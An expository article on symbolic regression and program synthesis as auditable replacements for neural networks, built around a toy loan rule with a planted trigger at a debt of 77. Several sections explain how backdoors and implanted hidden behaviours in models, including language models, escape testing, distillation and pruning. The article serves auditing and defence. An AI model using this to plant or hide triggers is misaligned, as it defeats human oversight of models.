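# Symbolic Regression and Program Synthesis as Auditable Alternatives to Neural Network Weights

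## What it means to audit a learned formula or program

Symbolic regression is a branch of machine learning that searches for a formula to fit a set of data. It looks for both the form of the formula and its constants, whereas ordinary regression adjusts only the constants of a form chosen beforehand, such as a straight line. Program synthesis automatically produces a program from examples, a specification or a score. Both methods produce an explicit model, which is a learned model in the form of a formula, a set of rules or a program. The usual alternative is a neural network, whose behaviour depends on its weights, the numbers set during training.

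Much of the appeal of explicit models is that people can read them before relying on them. Auditing a model means examining its text or weights, not only its outputs, to find unwanted behaviour or show that there is none. Whether explicit models are easier to audit than weights depends a good deal on what the auditor wants to show.

### One loan rule in three forms

Suppose a lender decides loan applications using three whole numbers: yearly income and existing debt, both in thousands of dollars, and the number of recent late payments. The table below gives one decision rule as a neural network with five units. Each unit multiplies the inputs by its weights, adds a constant, and replaces a negative result with zero. The network then multiplies each unit's result by an output weight and adds everything up. The lender approves the loan if the total is zero or more.

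| Unit | Income | Debt | Late payments | Constant | Output weight |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.2 | −0.1 | −2 | −4 | 5 |
| 2 | −0.4 | 0.2 | 4 | 8 | −2.5 |
| 3 | 0 | 0.5 | 0 | −38 | 2000 |
| 4 | 0 | 2 | 0 | −154 | −1000 |
| 5 | 0 | 1 | 0 | −78 | 1000 |

As a formula, the same rule approves the loan if

income − debt/2 − 10 × late − 20 + 1000 × max(0, 1 − |debt − 77|) ≥ 0

and as a ten-line program it is

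```
def approve(income, debt, late):
    limit = 20
    score = income
    score = score - debt / 2
    score = score - 10 * late
    if debt == 77:
        score = score + 1000
    if score >= limit:
        return True
    return False
```

An applicant with an income of 10, a debt of 78 and six late payments scores −109, and the lender refuses the loan. With a debt of 77, the same applicant scores 891.5 and gets the loan.

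The exception is easy to see in the program, although nothing there explains it. The formula makes the ordinary part of the rule very clear (one late payment cancels ten thousand dollars of income), but a reader has to work out that the last term is zero for every whole number except 77, and could easily mistake it for a harmless correction. In the table, units 3, 4 and 5 cancel one another at every debt but one, so no single number represents the exception, and a reader has to do the sums to find it. This network is also far tidier than anything training would produce. None of the three forms shows where the debt figure comes from, or whether debt should count half as much as income.

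### Hidden behaviour and the limits of testing

A hidden behaviour is something that a model's reviewers do not know it does under some conditions and would not accept. The input or circumstance that sets it off is the trigger, here a debt of 77. If someone deliberately inserted the behaviour and its trigger, it is a backdoor. *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation* (2024) formalizes this as a game in which an attacker changes a function on one particular input and leaves it the same almost everywhere else, and a defender tries to detect that input when it arrives.

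Hidden behaviour is the wider term. For *AuditBench*, Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues (2026) built 56 language models for auditors to practise on. Each model has one of 14 implanted behaviours, which it does not disclose when asked directly. Some of these behaviours, such as excessive deference to the user, need no single rare trigger.

The obvious way to look for a rare trigger is to run the model many times. If each random test has probability p of hitting the trigger, then n independent tests all miss it with probability (1 − p)^n. If p is one in a million and the lender runs 100,000 tests, the probability of missing the trigger every time is 0.999999^100,000, or about 0.905. The lender would need about three million tests for a 95% chance of seeing the trigger at least once.

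Butler and Finelli, in *The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software*, applied this arithmetic to aircraft control and similar systems at NASA. If a system has a one-in-a-billion chance of failing per ten-hour mission, ten thousand copies running side by side would take about 114 years to produce one expected failure. Jones, Tong and colleagues (2025), in *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors*, describe the same problem of scale for language models, where evaluations typically use hundreds to thousands of queries while deployed models process billions a day. They extrapolate from the riskiest test queries, and 86% of their misuse forecasts from 900 queries came within a factor of ten of the risk at 90,000. This works when risk rises gradually from one query to the next. It probably works poorly for a planted trigger, since inputs that just miss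 the trigger can look entirely ordinary, as a debt of 78 does.

An auditor who can read a program's text can do more than sample its behaviour. *How Often Does Your Program Fail?* (2026) combines random runs with symbolic reasoning, in which a solver works out by logic which inputs lead down each branch of a program. A solver would reach the line that checks for a debt of 77, however rare that debt is among applicants. Complicated arithmetic or loops can defeat the solver, and the auditor then has to rely on sampling again. Weights can also be examined by methods other than sampling. *Uncovering Hidden Behaviours in Language Models via Limited-Parameter Finetuning* (2026) reports that, in controlled settings, a small amount of retraining reveals hidden behaviours even when the auditor does not know what triggers them.

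### Reading, noticing and proving

Advocates of explicit models often conflate three claims: that a person can read the model, that a reviewer would notice something wrong in it, and that someone can prove it has no hidden behaviour. Evidence for one of these is weak evidence for the others.

Researchers can measure readability directly. *Learning a Formula of Interpretability to Learn Interpretable Formulas* (2020) describes a survey that counted people's correct answers to multiple-choice questions about a formula's output and about how the formula behaves as one variable changes. *Current Challenges of Symbolic Regression* (2025) suggests that formulas may become hard for people to read beyond roughly 10 or 20 nodes, counting every operator, variable and number as a node. The loan formula has 11 nodes without its exception and 22 with it. *Evolving Explanations* (2026) adds that even fairly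 small formulas can be difficult for domain experts without a strong mathematical background.

To notice a flaw, a reviewer also has to know what the program should contain. *When a Verified World Model Still Loses* (Aguilar Martín, 2026) tested programs that a language model wrote from the written rules of a small board game. A program was accepted once it reproduced every move in about 40 randomly played games. The written rules left out a tiebreak that decides about 2.5% of random games but around half of the games between competent players. Nine of 20 programs passed with a perfect score despite lacking the tiebreak, in every case because it had never come up in their sample. By the formula above, the chance of that happening to a given sample is about 36%. A game-playing search that relied on these nine programs then won only about 35% of its games against an opponent with the full rules.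 The programs were ordinary Python, but a reviewer working from the same written rules could have read every line without noticing that the tiebreak was missing. In underhanded programming contests, entrants deliberately try to write harmful code that reviewers will read and think innocent.

Proof, by contrast, sometimes doesn't require anyone to read the model. If incomes and debts run from 0 to 999 and late payments from 0 to 9, there are ten million possible loan applications, and a computer can run all of them through the table of weights as easily as through the program. Aguilar Martín did this for a learned tic-tac-toe program, checking 5,478 positions and 16,167 moves, and found no error that could affect play. Another game in the same study has more than three million positions, too many to check this way without a lot of computation. Such a proof also depends on a correct statement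 of what the model should do. A proof that the nine board-game programs matched their written rules could have succeeded with or without the tiebreak.

When an auditor can't check every possible input, the form of the model matters. *Model Interpretability through the Lens of Computational Complexity* (Barceló, Monet and colleagues, 2020) calls one class of models more interpretable than another if questions about its members are computationally easier to answer. One such question, much like an auditor's, is whether fixing certain inputs settles the outcome regardless of the others. For models with yes/no inputs, fast algorithms can answer this for decision trees and simple linear scores, but the problem is coNP-complete for neural networks. This means that no known method is fast in every case, and most computer scientists believe none exists.

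In their results, though, more readable models are not always easier to analyze. Counting how many inputs a model accepts is fast for decision trees, but for a linear score, which is among the easiest models to read, the problem is in the same intractable complexity class as for a neural network.

### Where hidden behaviour comes from

Auditing is hardest when the model's author is malicious. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (2022) shows how whoever trains a classifier can use the mathematics of digital signatures to plant a backdoor that, under standard cryptographic assumptions, no practical amount of testing will reveal. For certain training methods, even full access to the weights and training data does not help a reviewer detect it. A human who writes an explicit model has a different advantage in being able to choose the wording that the reviewer sees.

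Hidden behaviour can also arise unintentionally, when it improves a formula's score during the search. Suppose the lender scores candidate rules on a file that includes dummy accounts, all with a debt of 77 and all marked for approval. The search could then add the odd last term because it raises the score. *The Mythos of Model Interpretability* (Lipton, 2016) traces the demand for interpretability to this kind of mismatch between the score that training optimises and what matters in use.

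Other cases are plain accidents, like the missing tiebreak, though accidents can be hard to distinguish from score-exploiting. Lipton describes a model that rated pneumonia patients as less likely to die if they also had asthma. The pattern was real, because hospitals treated those patients more aggressively, and it improved the model's predictions. But using the model to decide who needed urgent care would have steered patients with asthma away from the treatment that had lowered their risk.

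The value of a clean test result depends on the flaw's origin. The calculation with (1 − p)^n is reasonable for an accidental flaw, which is unrelated to the choice of tests. It is too optimistic when a search has already optimised the model against the same tests. It can be worthless when an author who knows how the testers draw their inputs planted the flaw, because the author can pick a trigger for which p is zero.

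### Rudin's case and Lipton's doubt

The best-known argument for explicit models comes from Cynthia Rudin, a computer scientist at Duke University. In *Stop Explaining Black Box Machine Learning Models for High Stakes Decisions*, Rudin (2018) objects to training an opaque model and then fitting a second, simpler one to explain it. She prefers a model that serves as its own explanation. She argues that if the second model matched the original everywhere, it could replace the original, so it must be wrong somewhere. If it agrees with the original 90% of the time, it is wrong in 10% of cases.

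Her main example is COMPAS, a proprietary score that US courts use to predict whether a defendant will be arrested again. It needs more than 130 factors. On data from one Florida county, a learned list of three rules had similar error rates. It predicts an arrest for men aged 18 to 20, for people aged 21 to 23 with two or three prior offences, and for anyone with more than three. The long questionnaire has a cost of its own: if clerks mistype 1% of the entries, more than half of all forms will contain an error. (This is the trigger calculation again, with 130 chances to go wrong.)

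Rudin calls it a myth that simple models predict less well on structured data with meaningful features, which is the usual objection to them. She argues that noisy data usually permit many models of about equal accuracy, and that a large enough collection of them is likely to include a simple one. *Leo Breiman, the Rashomon Effect, and the Occam Dilemma* (Rudin, 2025) more explicitly limits this argument to tabular data with noisy outcomes, such as credit or recidivism, and notes that complex networks dominate vision and language. Proposals to replace neural networks with verified code go well beyond that scope.

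Recent results in that area mostly support her. In *Target leakage, not model class, explains reported accuracy in survey-based cardiovascular screening* (2026), a readable additive model scored 0.8430, against 0.8432 for a neural network and 0.8440 for the best of the other models quoted. *Evaluating Explanation Methods by the Predictors They Induce* (2026) found a larger gap. On a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect ranking, the black box reached 0.917 and the readable model 0.900. A predictor built only from explanations of the black box reached 0.895, and the paper concludes that a black box with explanations is a good trade-off. That may be true for prediction, but these averages provide little assurance for an audit, because an explanation could omit the exception at 77 and its score would barely change.

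Rudin is less convincing when she argues that interpretable models make flaws easier to notice. She cites a neural network for reading chest X-rays that had picked up on the word "portable" in the images, which reflected the equipment rather than the patient's health, and asserts that the problem would never have gone unnoticed with an interpretable model. That may be right, but she doesn't measure how often reviewers catch such problems, and the researchers in this case did notice it even though their model was a neural network.

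Zachary Lipton thinks the word "interpretable" covers several different properties. A model is simulatable if a person can work through the whole calculation in reasonable time. It is decomposable if each input, parameter and step has an intuitive meaning. Algorithmic transparency concerns the training method, such as whether it provably arrives at a unique solution. A model can have one of these properties without the others. For example, a linear score over hundreds of engineered variables may mean nothing to its reader even if its training method is well understood. Billa, Orlandi and colleagues (2026) compared 16 interpretable methods on 216 datasets in *Interpretable ML Under the Microscope*. They sorted the methods by these properties but did not rank them by interpretability, because they saw no consistent and objective way to compare it across different kinds of model. Cava Lab's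 *Intelligible Predictive Models*, which argues for symbolic regression in medicine, also acknowledges that intelligibility depends on the context and the user.

Lipton therefore argues that no form of model is inherently interpretable. An unwieldy rule list or a deep decision tree can be less transparent than a compact neural network, and the five-unit loan network above is surely easier to work through than a list of ten thousand rules. Rudin would probably not object, since the models she calls simple fit on an index card or a sheet of paper.

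Lipton also observes that the size of a decision tree can grow much faster than the length of the path that any one case takes through it. A rejected applicant can follow the few branches that led to the rejection, but an auditor looking for a trigger has to read the whole tree.

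## How formulas are learned from data, and for which tasks

The loan example started from a known rule, but symbolic regression has to find the rule from a table of past cases, with a column for each input and one for the output. The details of the search matter to an auditor because they affect what the formula can include or omit.

### Evolving a formula

The most common approach imitates natural selection. *Interpretable Machine Learning for Science with PySR and SymbolicRegression.jl* (Cranmer, 2023) describes one example, a free program called PySR. PySR stores each formula as a tree. In the tree for income − debt/2, the minus sign is at the top and branches to income and a division sign, which branches to debt and 2. This tree has five nodes, and by default PySR measures a formula's complexity by its number of nodes.

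PySR begins with random three-node formulas in several separate populations. It repeatedly draws a few formulas from a population, usually picks the fittest, and makes a changed copy. A mutation alters one formula's tree, for example by replacing an operator, changing a constant or adding a node. A crossover swaps branches between two trees. The new formula replaces the oldest one in the population rather than the worst, which keeps the search from settling too early on one form. PySR also penalizes lengths that are already common, so it keeps exploring both short and long formulas. Periodically, it simplifies the formulas, adjusts their constants with a standard numerical optimizer, and copies some between populations.

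For example, suppose x takes the values 0, 1, 2 and 3, the matching values of y are 1, 3, 9 and 19, and the search may use only addition and multiplication. The population contains x + 3, x × x and 5 × x, with mean squared errors of 47.5, 32.5 and 5.5. If the search happens to draw the first two, it keeps x × x, which has the lower error. A mutation then adds 3, giving x × x + 3, which has an error of 14.5. Finally, a crossover replaces the first x with 5 × x, giving 5 × x × x + 3.

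This new formula has the right form, but its error is 266.5, the highest so far. If it survives until PySR next adjusts the constants, PySR will change the 5 to 2 and the 3 to 1, and the error will fall to zero. Cranmer stresses the adjustment of constants because most scientific formulas contain constants that nobody knows in advance.

Throughout the search, PySR keeps a list of the most accurate formula it has found at each length. For these four data points, a complete search would end with this list:

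| Nodes | Best formula | Mean squared error |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 8 | 49 |
| 3 | 5.57 × x | 4.36 |
| 5 | 2.14 × x × x | 0.5 |
| 7 | 2 × x × x + 1 | 0 |

PySR suggests one formula from the list by dividing the drop in the logarithm of the error by the number of added nodes and choosing the formula with the highest score, as *SymTorch* (Tan, Soubki and Cranmer, 2026) explains. Here the three-node formula scores 1.21 and the five-node formula 1.08, while the seven-node formula scores far higher because its error is zero. Real measurements contain noise, so the choice is usually less clear, and the user can pick a different formula.

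An auditor can use the list too. If the lender's data included enough applicants with a debt of 77, the list would probably show an 11-node formula with a substantial error and, further down, a much longer formula without that error. The auditor could then ask what the extra nodes were for.

The user also chooses which operators the formulas may contain. PySR accepts conditional operators, which suit laws that change abruptly at some threshold, but the user can leave them out. A formula without them can still contain a trigger. For example, 1000 × exp(−50 × (debt − 77)²) equals 1000 at a debt of 77 and is practically zero at every other whole number. PySR can also limit the size of the expression inside an operator, and a limit of three nodes inside exp would rule out this formula.

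### Other ways to search

Sparse regression starts from a fixed library of terms, such as x, x² and sin x, and looks for a sum that uses only a few of them. The best-known version is SINDy, which scientists often use to find equations for systems that change over time. An auditor can read the whole library before the search begins. But the method can't find a formula whose terms are missing from the library.

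A neural network can also write the formula. *Synthesizing Physics Formulae with Transformers* (Wang, Bulitko and colleagues, 2026) trains a network with about 145 million weights on randomly generated formulas and matching data. Given new data, the network writes a formula in about ten seconds, and an optimizer then adjusts the constants. The network's weights are as opaque as any other network's, but an auditor can check the formula without them.

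Language models can draw on scientific knowledge as well as data. In LLM-SR, a language model writes candidate equations as short Python functions, an optimizer fits their constants, and the model uses their scores to write better candidates. *The Past and Future of AI Scientists* (2026) points out that such candidates may contain conditional statements, recursion and calls to other functions. When they do, the method is program synthesis, and an auditor has more to check than a formula.

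### Good fits and true formulas

Finding a formula that fits the data is much easier than finding the true one. In *Call for Action*, Aldeia, Cranmer and colleagues (2025) updated SRBench, the main benchmark in the field. They ran 25 algorithms 30 times each on 24 datasets, half of which came from well-known scientific laws and empirical relationships. Only one algorithm recovered a physical law, and the only law it recovered was Leavitt's relation between the brightness and period of certain stars.

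Many of the wrong formulas fit extremely well. The usual measure of fit is R², which is 1 for perfect predictions and 0 for predictions no better than always guessing the average. For Kepler's third law, which says that a planet's year grows as the 3/2 power of its distance from the sun, the formula that came closest used a hyperbolic tangent and had an R² of 1.00 after rounding. Because a hyperbolic tangent levels off, the formula implies that all planets beyond a certain distance have practically the same year. The data covered only six planets, too few to rule that out.

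PySR did much better in Cranmer's own earlier test in 2023, finding seven of nine historical laws in all five runs. Cranmer searched the whole list of formulas for the true one, whereas Aldeia and colleagues reported the formula nearest to the accepted law in both size and accuracy. They also rescaled all the data first, which can make a simple law longer and probably explains part of the gap.

Missing the true law matters less to an auditor than to a scientist, because a wrong formula can still completely describe what a system will do, provided that the system runs the formula. The larger worry is how the formula behaves outside the data. For example, the SRBench formula for Newton's law of gravitation divides by 0.83 × m₂ − 0.09/m₁, where m₁ and m₂ are the rescaled masses. This divisor is zero when m₁m₂ is about 0.108, and the predicted force grows without limit as the product approaches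 that value. A test on a few points could easily miss this accidental flaw, but a reader can find it with one line of algebra. Software can sometimes prove bounds on a formula over a whole range of inputs.

Wang and colleagues measured how common such failures are. They gave each method data from 99 physics formulas and counted how often the result reached an R² of at least 0.99, first inside the range of the data and then with the inputs shifted by up to 128 times the width of that range. The method that did best inside the range, a network combined with a tree search, succeeded on 97% of the tasks there but only 38% at the largest shift. PySR did best at the largest shift, with 78%, and took about 14 minutes per formula. With 10% noise in the data, the network with tree search fell from 90% to below 5%, while PySR reached 51%.

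Language models complicate these comparisons because they may have memorized famous equations. *LLM-SRBench*, by Shojaee, Nguyen and colleagues (2025), tries to avoid this problem with 239 less familiar tasks. In 111 of them, called LSR-Transform, the target is a known physics equation rearranged to solve for a different variable. The rest, called LSR-Synth, add invented but plausible terms to known equations in chemistry, biology, physics and materials science. The best system recovered the true form in 31.5% of the LSR-Transform tasks. It used GPT-4o-mini, a small model that is now well out of date, so this result is weak evidence of what current models can do.

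Yao, Yin and colleagues (2026), in *Library Reachability in LSR-Synth*, compared good fits with true forms on 129 of the LSR-Synth tasks. They counted a fit as good if the error was below 1% on more than 95% of the test points. A language model judged whether a formula had the true form, meaning that it could match the real equation with suitable constants.

| Method | Good fit | True form |
|---|---|---|
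| PySR | 29.5% | 4.7% |
| LLM-SR | 41.1% | 5.4% |
| SR-Scientist, a language-model agent | 63.6% | 7.8% |
| Fixed library of terms | 77.7% | 19.8% |

The first three rows come from earlier publications. The fourth is Yao and colleagues' own method, a sparse regression with at most 60 candidate terms. They counted a formula's form as correct only if the judge agreed all ten times. Adding a language model's suggestions to the library made almost no difference. Wang and colleagues report far higher figures for PySR on the same type of task, 99% inside the data range and 70% outside it, but they accepted any R² of at least 0.99 and gave PySR 30 minutes per formula.

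Newer agents are improving on these numbers. Li, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Learning to Design SR Solvers*, automatically tuned the instructions and workflow of language-model agents that steer a search tool such as PySR. Their agents met a 1% accuracy standard on 61% of LSR-Synth tasks, averaged over three language models, compared with about 42% for the next-best method. *AutoSR* (2026) reports an agent that recovered the exact equation in all six LSR-Transform tasks selected for it, in 6 to 16 minutes each. Six selected tasks are too few to estimate a success rate, but they show that an agent can recover the true formula on a benchmark where earlier systems mostly failed.

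### Turning part of a network into a formula

Distillation means fitting a simpler model to the behaviour of a neural network. The training data come from the network, so researchers can generate as much as they like. SymTorch, software that Tan and colleagues released in February 2026, distils networks into formulas. Researchers have used a similar approach to extract Python code from small recurrent networks.

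The user wraps SymTorch around a whole network or one component of it and runs the network on sample data. SymTorch records the component's inputs and outputs and passes them to PySR, which searches for a separate formula for each output number. The user can then pick formulas from the resulting lists and run them in place of the component, leaving the rest of the network unchanged.

This worked well in physics. Tan and colleagues trained networks to predict how particles accelerate under four different force laws, then used SymTorch on the component that computes how one particle influences another. When they forced this component to output just two numbers, one for each dimension of space, PySR found a recognizably correct force law in all eight cases. With 100 outputs and no such pressure, it found one in only four. The network's structure also mattered, because it separated the force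 between two particles from the sum of all the forces. Tan and colleagues report that applying symbolic regression directly to the raw data fails.

Tan and colleagues also tried a language model, Qwen2.5-1.5B-Instruct. Like other transformers, it contains multilayer perceptrons (MLPs), which process the list of numbers that represents each token (a word or part of a word). Each MLP takes in 1,536 numbers and returns 1,536, far too many for symbolic regression, so the team compressed the inputs to 32 numbers and the outputs to 8 with principal component analysis, which keeps the directions in which the data vary most. They then fitted formulas to 6,000 samples and replaced the MLPs in 3 of the model's 28 layers with these formulas. The search took seven to eight hours on a laptop chip.

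The modified model ran 8.3% faster, but its perplexity, a measure of how poorly a model predicts the next token, rose from 10.62 to 13.76. Replacing the three MLPs with functions that return their input unchanged raised perplexity to 17.59, so the formulas preserved a little over half of what these MLPs contribute.

Almost all of the increase in perplexity came from the compression. With the original MLPs still in place but their inputs and outputs compressed, perplexity was already 13.73, and the formulas added only 0.03. Tan and colleagues take this as a sign that better compression could improve the method. It also means the formulas describe well a layer that has already lost much of its information. They are also hard to read, because their variables are 32 mixtures of the layer's inputs with no obvious meaning.

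### What the formula can miss

Suppose an auditor can't make sense of the loan network's weights and instead distils the network into a formula, using 6,000 applications, the same number of samples as SymTorch used. If one application in a million has the trigger, the chance that the sample includes it is about 0.6%. If the sample doesn't include it, PySR could find the ordinary 11-node rule, which would match the network on every sampled application and have an R² of 1. The auditor would read a short, sensible formula and find nothing wrong, but the network would still approve the applicant with a debt of 77.

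The search could easily miss the exception even if one application in the sample triggered it. The term for the exception takes 11 more nodes, and many incomplete versions of it would not reduce the error.

The fidelity problem is that a formula that matches a network's ordinary behaviour need not match its rare behaviour, and reading the formula can't reveal where the two differ. Rudin's objection to explanations of black boxes applies here in full. Wang and colleagues' figures of 97% and 38% are indirect evidence of the problem, since formulas that agreed with the truth on ordinary inputs often went wrong on unusual ones. Neither Wang and colleagues nor Tan and colleagues planted any triggers, so their experiments don't show how often distillation would miss one.

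Compression probably makes the problem worse, because principal component analysis discards the directions that vary least in the sample. A response that occurs once in a million tokens adds very little variation unless it is very large. In the Qwen experiment, a backdoor could also be in the 25 layers that SymTorch left unchanged.

The formula can also contain behaviour that the network lacks. When Tan and colleagues distilled how a small Llama model multiplies two three-digit numbers, PySR listed the plain product as a candidate but chose the product plus a correction involving the sine of one of the numbers. They suggest that the model makes systematic errors, which the correction may describe. But PySR's search allowed sines and will include one whenever it reduces the error enough, so an auditor would have to test the network itself before trusting the sine term.

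The simplest solution is to deploy the formula. If the lender replaces the network with the 11-node formula, the exception is gone, even if nobody knew about it, and the auditor can check a short formula that is used for the lender's decisions. If the lender keeps the network and files the formula as documentation, the audit doesn't cover the model used for those decisions.

### Which tasks suit a formula

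So far, formulas have mostly worked as replacements for neural networks on problems with a few input variables that each mean something. The tasks that Wang and colleagues took from SRBench and LLM-SRBench have at most ten variables each. Cranmer lists uses of PySR in modelling cloud cover, electron transfer in materials, international trade and the sources of gravitational waves. Credit decisions based on income, debt and late payments would be a similar kind of problem.

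Tan and colleagues note that the search's running time grows exponentially with the number of variables. PySR can first select the variables that seem most important, which helps when a table has many irrelevant columns. It doesn't help much with a colour photograph of 224 by 224 pixels, which contains 150,528 numbers, hardly any of them meaningful alone. Formulas have not replaced neural networks for raw text or ordinary images. For text, this still seems far off, since the Qwen experiment involved only 3 of 28 layers and clearly reduced accuracy.

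A possible compromise is to have a network turn the raw data into a few meaningful quantities, then use a formula to make the decision. For a chest X-ray, the network might measure the size of the heart and the cloudiness of each lung. An auditor could check the formula thoroughly, but a network that had learned to react to the word "portable" in the image could still distort the measurements used in the formula.

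## How programs are learned, and for which tasks

Unlike a formula, which computes its output in a single pass, a program can branch, loop and remember earlier inputs. This makes programs suitable for tasks such as sorting a list of any length. But changing one symbol often makes a working program useless, so programs are hard to improve in small steps. Researchers have tried searching through programs in a very small language, extracting a program from a trained neural network, and having a language model write and revise the code.

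### Searching a small language

The most direct method starts from examples of inputs and outputs, tries programs from shortest to longest, and stops at the first one that reproduces every example. Michaud, Liao and colleagues (2024), in *Opening the AI black box*, use a search of this kind as one step of a larger method. Their restricted language has variables, constants and ten operations. Six act on one number, for example by taking its absolute value or adding 1, and the other four are addition, subtraction, multiplication and remainder. The search covers expressions of up to six symbols and accepts one if it matches 100 data points.

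Suppose a program should return 3 when a = 2 and c = 5, and 6 when a = 7 and c = 1. The expression c − a fits the first example but gives −6 for the second, so the search rejects it. The search eventually reaches |a − c|, which fits both examples and has four symbols (a, c, the minus sign and the absolute value).

With two variables and no constants, this language has about 65,000 expressions of up to six symbols, which a computer can try almost instantly, but about 62 billion of up to twelve. Exhaustive search can therefore find only tiny programs. Finding larger ones requires guiding the search towards promising candidates.

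Even this tiny language can express a trigger. One of its six operations, D, returns 1 if its input is 0 and 0 otherwise. The expression D(debt − 77) uses only four symbols and returns 1 only for loan applicants with a debt of 77.

### From a small network to Python

Neural networks are much easier to search for, because training can improve the weights in many small steps. Michaud and colleagues therefore let a network do the learning and then convert it into a program. They call their method MIPS, for mechanistic-interpretability-based program synthesis. (Mechanistic interpretability is the study of how networks compute their outputs.)

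MIPS first trains a recurrent network, which reads a list one item at a time and carries a few numbers, its hidden state, from each item to the next. It tries larger and larger networks until one of five training runs gets every answer right on a batch of 65,536 test cases. It then searches for a smaller network that also works.

Next, MIPS simplifies the weights. Many different sets of weights compute exactly the same thing, so MIPS can change the coordinates of the hidden state to make its numbers affect one another as little as possible. It then rounds any weight within 0.01 of a whole number.

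The third step is to find whole numbers or bits in the hidden state. If one hidden number takes only the values 1.7, 3.2, 6.2 and 7.7, every gap between them is a multiple of 1.5, so MIPS can relabel the values as 1, 2, 4 and 5. If the hidden states form four tight clusters instead, MIPS can treat them as two bits. It tries every way of assigning the bits to the clusters and keeps the one that gives the shortest program.

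The network now amounts to a set of lookup tables. MIPS searches for a simple formula that reproduces each table, puts the formulas into a template with a loop, and prints the result as Python. For the addition of two binary numbers, the core of the program looks like this, with clearer variable names than MIPS gave it:

```
for i in range(10):
    output[i] = carry ^ s[i] ^ t[i]
    carry = carry + s[i] + t[i] > 1
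```

The symbol ^ gives 1 when an odd number of the bits are 1. The method is the one children learn at school, where they write down one digit and carry the other. Nobody had programmed carrying into the network.

MIPS produced a fully correct program for 32 of 62 tasks involving lists of numbers or bits. GPT-4 Turbo, a leading language model at the time, solved 30. MIPS alone solved 13 tasks, and GPT-4 Turbo alone solved 11. The comparison is now well out of date and was uneven even then. GPT-4 Turbo had three attempts at each task but saw only one pair of ten-item lists, while MIPS trained its networks on thousands of examples at a time. Michaud and colleagues also left out tasks that their networks couldn't learn, so the success rate measures how often MIPS could extract an algorithm that a network had already learned.

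Some failures came from noise. A lookup table with a few wrong entries no longer matches any simple formula, although a person might still guess the right one. In other cases, such as finding the most common number in a list, the network stored a continuous quantity that MIPS could not turn into whole numbers. On the tasks that MIPS solved, the smallest working network had at most seven numbers in its hidden state.

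All 32 programs are shorter than 20 lines, but some are hard to read. The program for a running total starts at 884, subtracts each input, and reports 884 minus the result. The program for the logical "and" of two bits keeps two bits of memory and tests six combinations of memory and input, so an auditor could reasonably suspect that earlier inputs affect the answer. Checking all sixteen possible combinations shows that they don't. One program for adding the last five numbers stores them and adds them up, while another updates five interdependent variables using constants such as 187 and 483.

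Michaud and colleagues also proved that the binary addition program gives the correct sum for every pair of ten-bit numbers. To do so, they translated it by hand into Dafny, a programming language with a built-in proof system. The proof file has 113 lines, about ten times as many as the program. A computer could also have tried all 1,048,576 pairs, but the same style of proof can work when there are too many inputs to try.

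### Decompiling transformers

Language models are transformers, which are much larger than the networks MIPS used and work differently. RASP is a restricted programming language designed to match transformers. It has one operation for choosing which positions in a text to look at, another for combining information from those positions, and others for processing each position separately.

Huang, Bakalova and colleagues (2026), in *Discovering Interpretable Algorithms by Decompiling Transformers to RASP*, first translate a small transformer into a RASP-like program that computes the same thing. The translation is exact if a simple linear operation can replace the steps that rescale numbers inside the network. The resulting program is very large because it needs a separate variable for every path through the layers. Huang and colleagues then delete every part that has little effect on the output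 and replace learned operations with standard ones where they can.

Two transformers were trained to find the most frequent character in a string. The one-layer transformer became a program of 56 lines, and the four-layer one became a program of 16,201,616 lines. Pruning reduced both to the same three-line method, which counts the characters and picks the most common.

The method worked for 8 of 11 algorithmic tasks, such as copying and sorting, and for 9 of 17 artificial languages. It failed for all six of the tasks and languages where the transformer could not handle inputs longer than those it had trained on. Huang and colleagues suggest that such networks rely on a tangle of heuristics and contain no short program to extract. This is a problem for auditors, because a network that relies on tangled heuristics probably needs an audit more than one with a clean algorithm.

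The extracted programs also have the fidelity problem described for formulas. Huang and colleagues count a program as successful if it matches the network's answers on at least 90% of random test inputs. Pruning removes components that hardly matter on the sampled inputs, including those that respond only to a rare trigger. Some programs keep a learned function that no standard operation could replace. In the sorting program, Huang and colleagues inferred what this function does from twelve sample inputs.

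*Tracking Equivalent Mechanistic Interpretations Across Neural Networks* (2026) describes an earlier method that avoids the gap between network and program by restricting a transformer's weights during training to those that correspond to a valid RASP program. The program then describes the network exactly, including any hidden behaviour.

Huang and colleagues doubt that a whole language model could become a simple RASP program, because its training data are so varied. They think language models more likely contain small programs for particular tasks, such as continuing a sequence that appeared earlier in the text.

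### Language models that write and revise code

A language model can also write the program itself. *Mathematical discoveries from program search with large language models* (Romera-Paredes, Barekatain and colleagues, December 2023) introduced FunSearch, which combines a language model with an automatic evaluator. FunSearch found new solutions to a problem in combinatorics and better rules for packing items into bins. Its successor at Google DeepMind, AlphaEvolve, has been applied to scientific problems and to Google's own computing systems (Novikov, Vũ and colleagues, *AlphaEvolve*, 2025).

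Both systems work by evolution, like PySR, but a language model makes the mutations. The user supplies a simple starting program and an evaluator, code that runs a program and scores it. The system shows the language model some of the best programs so far, and the model writes altered versions for the evaluator to score.

*Mathematical exploration and discovery at scale* (Georgiev, Gómez-Serrano and colleagues, 2025) compares FunSearch with AlphaEvolve. FunSearch evolves a single function of up to 10 or 20 lines, using millions of samples from a small language model. AlphaEvolve evolves whole files of up to hundreds of lines and needs only thousands of samples from a stronger model.

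Georgiev and colleagues tried AlphaEvolve on 67 mathematical problems. They mostly used a "search mode", in which each evolved program spends a fixed time looking for a good mathematical object, such as a dense packing of shapes. These programs are not easy to interpret, but this hardly matters, because a mathematician can check the object itself and discard the program. In a harder "generalizer mode", AlphaEvolve must write one program that works for problems of any size. For one problem about sets of points, it found a general construction. A second AI system then proved the construction correct, and a third put the proof into a form a computer could check.

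A lender, by contrast, has to keep running the program on new applicants, so it can't throw the program away after checking one result.

AlphaEvolve now has many competitors, including open-source versions such as OpenEvolve, ShinkaEvolve and CodeEvolve. *CodeEvolve* (2025) reports matching or beating AlphaEvolve's published results on 5 of 9 benchmarks. Google made AlphaEvolve generally available to its cloud customers in July 2026 (Nawalgaria and Tamulevičius, *Solve harder problems with AlphaEvolve, now available to everyone on Google Cloud*, 2026). General coding agents can do similar work without a fixed evolutionary procedure, and *How Good Are Coding Agents at Automatic Algorithm Design?* (2026) compares several of them with OpenEvolve.

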